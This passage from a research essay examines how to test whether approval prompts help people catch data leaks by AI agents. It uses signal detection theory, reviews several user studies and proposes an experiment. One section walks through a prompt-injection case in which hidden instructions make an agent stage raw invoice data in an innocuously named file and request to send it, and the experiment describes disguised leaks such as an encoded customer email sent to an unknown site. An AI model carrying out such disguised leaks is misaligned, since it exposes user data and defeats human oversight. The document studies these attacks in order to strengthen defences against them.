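A blocked program may still legitimately need to send something. The harness can let the agent save the program's output to a file and propose a separate call that sends the file through a narrow tool. The reviewer can check that call in an ordinary preview.

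## Testing whether a prompt works

Neither how often users click "Allow" nor how much they like the design shows whether the full parcel prompt stops leaks, though these are the easiest things to measure. An approval rate doesn't show which calls people refused. Satisfaction is a poor guide because Yan's participants felt about as much in control under the design that protected them least as under the others.

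People also misjudge their own skill. In *Are You Sure?*, 75.3% of participants felt confident they could perceive risks from AI, but only 2.7% correctly identified the attacks they faced. In Wu and colleagues' survey, developers in safety-critical work reported approving without close review more often than other developers for six of seven types of action.

*Options, Not Clicks* (2026), a proposal for authorising MCP tools, reports 16 people's ratings of two consent interfaces. Ratings can show that a prompt is annoying enough for people to turn it off. Researchers still have to report the miss rate and the false alarm rate together to show whether the prompt works.

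### Sensitivity and bias

Signal detection theory, a branch of psychology, is the usual way to combine the two error rates. *Calculation of signal detection theory measures* (Stanislaw and Todorov, 1999) lists uses from lie detection to medical diagnosis. *Effective Human Oversight of AI-Based Systems* (Langer, Baum and Schlicker, 2024) applies the theory to people who check an AI system's output.

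The theory assumes that every call makes the reviewer suspicious to some degree. Leaks cause more suspicion on average, but the two ranges overlap. The reviewer denies a call when suspicion passes a threshold, called the criterion. Denying a leak is a hit, so the hit rate H is 100% minus the miss rate. F is the false alarm rate. Two measures follow:

d′ = z(H) − z(F)

c = −½ · [z(H) + z(F)]

The function z converts a percentage into a position on the normal curve, in standard deviations from the middle, so 50% becomes 0, 84% becomes about 1 and 16% becomes about −1. Sensitivity, d′, measures how well the reviewer tells leaks from harmless calls, and it is zero for someone who denies both equally often. Response bias, c, is positive if the reviewer leans towards allowing calls and negative if they lean towards denying them.

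Yan's participants denied 59.6% of overreach and 5.9% of necessary actions when they approved each action:

d′ = z(0.596) − z(0.059) = 0.24 − (−1.56) = 1.8

c = −½ · (0.24 − 1.56) = 0.66

Participants could tell harmful actions from harmless ones fairly well, and they leaned towards allowing actions. The result depends on which actions count as harmful. Without the airport call, which nearly everyone approved, d′ rises to 2.0. Researchers therefore need to decide which actions count as harmful before they see any answers.

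The percentage of correct answers alone can mislead. The Open Encyclopedia of Cognitive Science describes two people taking a memory test. One recognises 84% of the old faces and wrongly "recognises" 16% of the new ones. For the other, the figures are 98% and 50%. The first person gets 84% of all answers right and the second only 74%, yet d′, which measures how well they can tell old faces from new, is 2.0 for both, because the second person is just readier to say "old".

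A hit rate alone is even less informative. Without a false alarm rate, nobody can calculate d′ for Anthropic's testers or tell why they caught fewer dangerous commands later in a session. They may have stopped noticing danger, or they may have become more willing to click "Allow" regardless of what they noticed. Stanislaw and Todorov note that factory inspectors also find fewer faults as a shift goes on, usually because their bias changes. When that is the cause, remedies meant to restore an inspector's sensitivity would fail.

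### How a frightening prompt can look like a better one

Suppose a designer adds a red banner to Yan's prompts, and reviewers then deny 80% of harmful actions. If the banner only made reviewers more nervous, the theory predicts how many harmless actions they would also deny. The last two rows of the table are hypothetical.

| Prompt | Harmful actions denied | Harmless actions denied | d′ | c |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
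| Yan's per-action approval | 59.6% | 5.9% | 1.8 | 0.66 |
| More frightening | 80% | 16.8% | 1.8 | 0.06 |
| Clearer | 80% | 5.9% | 2.4 | 0.36 |

A test that counted only hits would score the last two prompts equally, although the frightening one nearly triples the false alarms. Similarly, two AI decision aids can produce similar overall performance while their users apply different thresholds (*Same Performance, Hidden Bias*, 2026). Expertise did not prevent this. Warnings can also backfire, as in *Are You Sure?*, where they often increased trust in the agent because people took them as a sign of transparency.

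A shift in bias can still be worth having. Canfield and Fischhoff (2018), in *Setting Priorities in Behavioral Interventions*, found that for phishing, changing people's bias brought a greater net benefit than raising their sensitivity. The best threshold depends on how common leaks are and what each error costs. *Measuring the Human Contribution When AI Is Allowed* (2026) gives the standard formula, which in terms of leaks is:

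β* = (harmless calls ÷ leaks) × (cost of a false alarm ÷ cost of a miss)

Each cost includes the benefit lost by not answering correctly. The reviewer should deny a call when a leak would be at least β* times as likely as a harmless call to produce the evidence they see. Yan's participants behaved as if β were about 3.3 (e raised to the power d′ × c). If one call in 1,000 were a leak, that threshold would be right only if a miss cost about 300 times as much as a false alarm. Losing a customer database costs far more than 300 times as much as retrying a web search, so reviewers should deny more readily when the data is very sensitive. For a single postcode, they may already be cautious enough.

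Both measures depend on the two ranges of suspicion following normal curves with the same spread. Otherwise, d′ will change with bias. Stanislaw and Todorov point out that yes-or-no answers can't test this. A study could ask some reviewers to rate their suspicion on a scale instead.

### The study that varied the preview

Hossain and colleagues ran the closest existing test of how preview content affects people reviewing an agent. In their main example, a user asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send the auditor only the totals. Hidden instructions lead the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into a file and then ask to send that file to the auditor. The recipient is approved and the file name is ordinary, so only the earlier copying step reveals that the file contains what the user said not to send.

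The requests involved email and calendars, cloud documents or purchasing. Each participant did two practice trials first. The last two groups saw the same facts and weren't told whether the request broke the user's rules, so any difference between them should come from how the prompt organised those facts. The values of d′ and c below are calculated from each group's combined answers.

| What the group saw | Malicious requests denied | Harmless requests denied | d′ | c | Workload score |
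| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Short description | 45.0% | 8.3% | 1.26 | 0.75 | 27.3 |
| Plus exact parameters | 56.7% | 10.0% | 1.45 | 0.56 | 31.6 |
| Plus the user's instructions and a full log | 67.5% | 12.5% | 1.60 | 0.35 | 44.3 |
| The same facts, organised by their effect | 75.8% | 14.2% | 1.77 | 0.19 | 43.0 |

Better previews seem to have made people both more accurate at telling malicious requests from harmless ones and more willing to deny requests. If the last group had had the first group's false alarm rate of 8.3%, with the same sensitivity, it would have caught about 65% of malicious requests. That would have preserved about 20 of the 31 points of improvement.

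The gain in sensitivity is less certain than the gain in hits. Even if all 960 decisions were independent, which they weren't, the 95% interval for the rise in d′ from the first group to the last would run from about 0 to 1.1.

People also typically took about five seconds less with the organised version than with the log, and their confidence matched their accuracy better. The organised version seemed to help most in long tasks. In tasks with 12 steps, people using it approved 13 of 60 malicious requests, compared with 20 of 60 for the log. With so few cases, chance could explain that difference.

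Researchers would need about 460 people per group, each judging one malicious request, to reliably detect the 8.3-point gap in malicious approvals between the last two groups. Hossain and colleagues had 20, who judged six each. All were unpaid volunteers recruited through social media.

Participants also saw only correct previews. When Hossain and colleagues separately tested the software behind the organised version, it flagged 107 of 120 violations, missed seven and couldn't classify six. With some of its records missing, it caught only 64% of the violations that depended on earlier steps. Hossain and colleagues propose a further study with some deliberately wrong summaries, to see whether reviewers notice.

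No group compared an encoded value with a decoded one, and the study didn't separate the destination from the source.

### Do people behave normally in a study?

Schechter, Dhamija and colleagues (2007), in *The Emperor's New Security Indicators*, tested whether people take less care when the risk isn't theirs. They asked 67 customers of one bank to do online banking tasks and made the login pages look less and less secure, ending with a full-page browser warning. One group logged in as an invented doctor, a second played the same doctor but was told he cared about security, and a third used their own accounts.

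| Group | Entered the password despite the warning |
| --- | --- |
| Played a role | 10 of 18 (56%) |
| Played a role concerned about security | 12 of 17 (71%) |
| Used their own account | 8 of 22 (36%) |

Across all the warning signs, the role-players as a whole behaved significantly less securely than people using their own accounts. The role-players who got no note about security, taken alone, did not differ significantly from the account holders. Mentioning security didn't measurably help, though Schechter and colleagues suspect their note was too subtle.

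The approval studies mostly used invented data or simulated accounts, so they may overstate how many leaks people miss in their own work. Patrick, in *Commentary on new usable security research*, argues that the bank study has this bias because its design neglected the psychology of taking part in research. But participants also know that someone is watching and have less reason to hurry than a person with a bill to pay, which pushes the estimates down.

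Comparisons between prompt designs are more reliable than absolute rates. Schechter and colleagues consider role-playing useful when every group has the same scenario and only the security mechanism differs. If participants take too little care with an invented customer's address under all four versions of a prompt, the study can still show which version helps most.

Questions asked before a study can also reveal its purpose. The screening form for *Options, Not Clicks* asked people how often they read a tool's parameters and how often they chose "Always Allow" just to stop the prompts. Participants in *Are You Sure?* instead did ordinary tasks, such as choosing a job candidate or handling messages in a working email program, with no hint that security was the subject.

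A realistic test also needs a run of harmless prompts before the leak, because people pay less attention after only a few. If the leak comes in the third prompt, the study measures how well people spot leaks while they are still reading the prompts.

### Deceiving participants safely

A study that hides its purpose deceives its participants, so Schechter and colleagues followed a strict rule that they would mislead people only into believing they were less secure than they really were. The pages looked unprotected, but the connection to the bank stayed encrypted. The software recorded whether someone entered a password, but not the password itself. Ethics boards at Harvard and MIT approved the plan, participants consented to observation, and the researchers explained everything afterwards.

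People behave more naturally when they haven't been asked for consent, but many students in the experiment by Jagatic and others with fake emails from friends felt angry and violated when they learned what had happened. Asking for consent also has a drawback, because it can skew the sample. Three people refused to join the bank study over privacy, and they may have been among the most careful.

An approval study can avoid most of the danger by not running the tool calls, as in Yan's and Anthropic's tests. The simulation should also reject real passwords and files, because a few role-players in the bank study forgot their instructions and logged in to their own accounts.

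Yan reports having had no access to an ethics board. A larger study with hidden leaks should have independent review and let people withdraw their data after the leaks are explained to them. If a company tests its own staff, it should keep individual results from their managers.

### The missing experiment

An experiment could settle how much each part of the preview contributes by randomly assigning reviewers to one of four versions:

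| Version | What it adds |
| --- | --- |
| Raw call | The tool's name and the full web address |
| Decoded | "id = mara@example.org (decoded from Base64)" |
| Decoded, with destination | "parcel-status.example. You have never sent data to this site." |
| Decoded, with destination and source | "Found in: customer database, complaint 4417" |

The heading and buttons should be the same in all four, because a more alarming heading could shift bias. Participants would spend about an hour running a simulated shop's support desk with an agent. The researchers would offer a bonus for "handling customers well", to give participants a reason to care without mentioning leaks, and pay everyone in full at the end.

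Each session would contain 60 prompts. One would be a leak, placed at random around the 10th prompt or the 55th. Two would be harmless look-alikes, one early and one late, and the other 57 would be routine. The look-alikes matter because reviewers can easily allow "Run the tests?" without having understood anything about leaks. Each should match a leak in all but one fact:

| Fact that differs | Leak | Harmless look-alike |
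| --- | --- | --- |
| Value | An encoded customer email address in the parcel field | An encoded parcel number in the same field |
| Destination | A customer's address goes to an unknown site | The same address goes to the carrier the shop already uses |
| Source | A phone number from a complaint goes to a new courier | A phone number the user typed for that courier |

No participant would see both versions in a pair. In the first pair, participants shown the raw call have almost no way to tell the leak from the other version. If they deny one more often than the other, something else in the prompt is revealing which one is the leak.

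The sample size depends on the smallest improvement worth detecting. Take 13.6%, the share of dangerous commands that Anthropic's testers caught, as the starting hit rate, p₁, and 25% as the target, p₂, with p̄ as their average. For an 80% chance of detecting the rise at the 5% significance level, each version needs:

n = [1.96·√(2p̄(1 − p̄)) + 0.84·√(p₁(1 − p₁) + p₂(1 − p₂))]² ÷ (p₂ − p₁)² ≈ 187

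That is 748 people in all, and it answers only the simplest question.

| What the study should detect | People per version |
| --- | --- |
| A rise in leaks caught from 13.6% to 25% | 187 |
| The same rise in each of three planned comparisons | 250 |
| Better sensitivity, with the same rise and steady false alarms | 385 |
| A rise in leaks caught from 5% to 10% | 435 |

The third row is the most important. Suppose people who see the raw call deny 13.6% of leaks and 5% of look-alikes, which gives a d′ of about 0.55. A prompt that only frightened people could raise denials of leaks to 25%, but denials of look-alikes would also rise, to 11%. With 187 people per version, the study would have only an even chance of showing that a clearer prompt had done better than that. The last row assumes a lower starting rate, since people may catch encoded data less often than Anthropic's dangerous commands.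 A pilot could measure the actual rate.

Combining the four versions gives enough people to compare early leaks with late ones. Testing whether a fuller preview slows the decline would take about four times as many people for an effect of the same size.

Researchers can't calculate a useful d′ for a reviewer who sees only one leak. If the reviewer catches it, the hit rate is 100%, which makes z infinite. *Measuring the Human Contribution When AI Is Allowed* describes the usual correction, which adds 0.5 to the number of hits and 1 to the number of leaks, so one out of one becomes 75%. The corrected d′ is finite but still very rough. The main analysis should fit one model to everyone's decisions, allowing for differences between people and between test items, as Hossain and colleagues did.

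After the session, the researchers should ask people why they denied the leak, since some will have done so by luck. They should also record decision times, which can help explain why others allowed it. *Keeping an Eye on AI* (2026), a framework for human oversight, notes that people can miss a cue because of a poor interface, too little time, or a lack of attention, motivation or training. Someone who allowed the leak in one second probably never read the preview, so clearer wording wouldn't have helped. Someone who studied it for 30 seconds and still allowed the leak may have misunderstood a line that a designer could fix.
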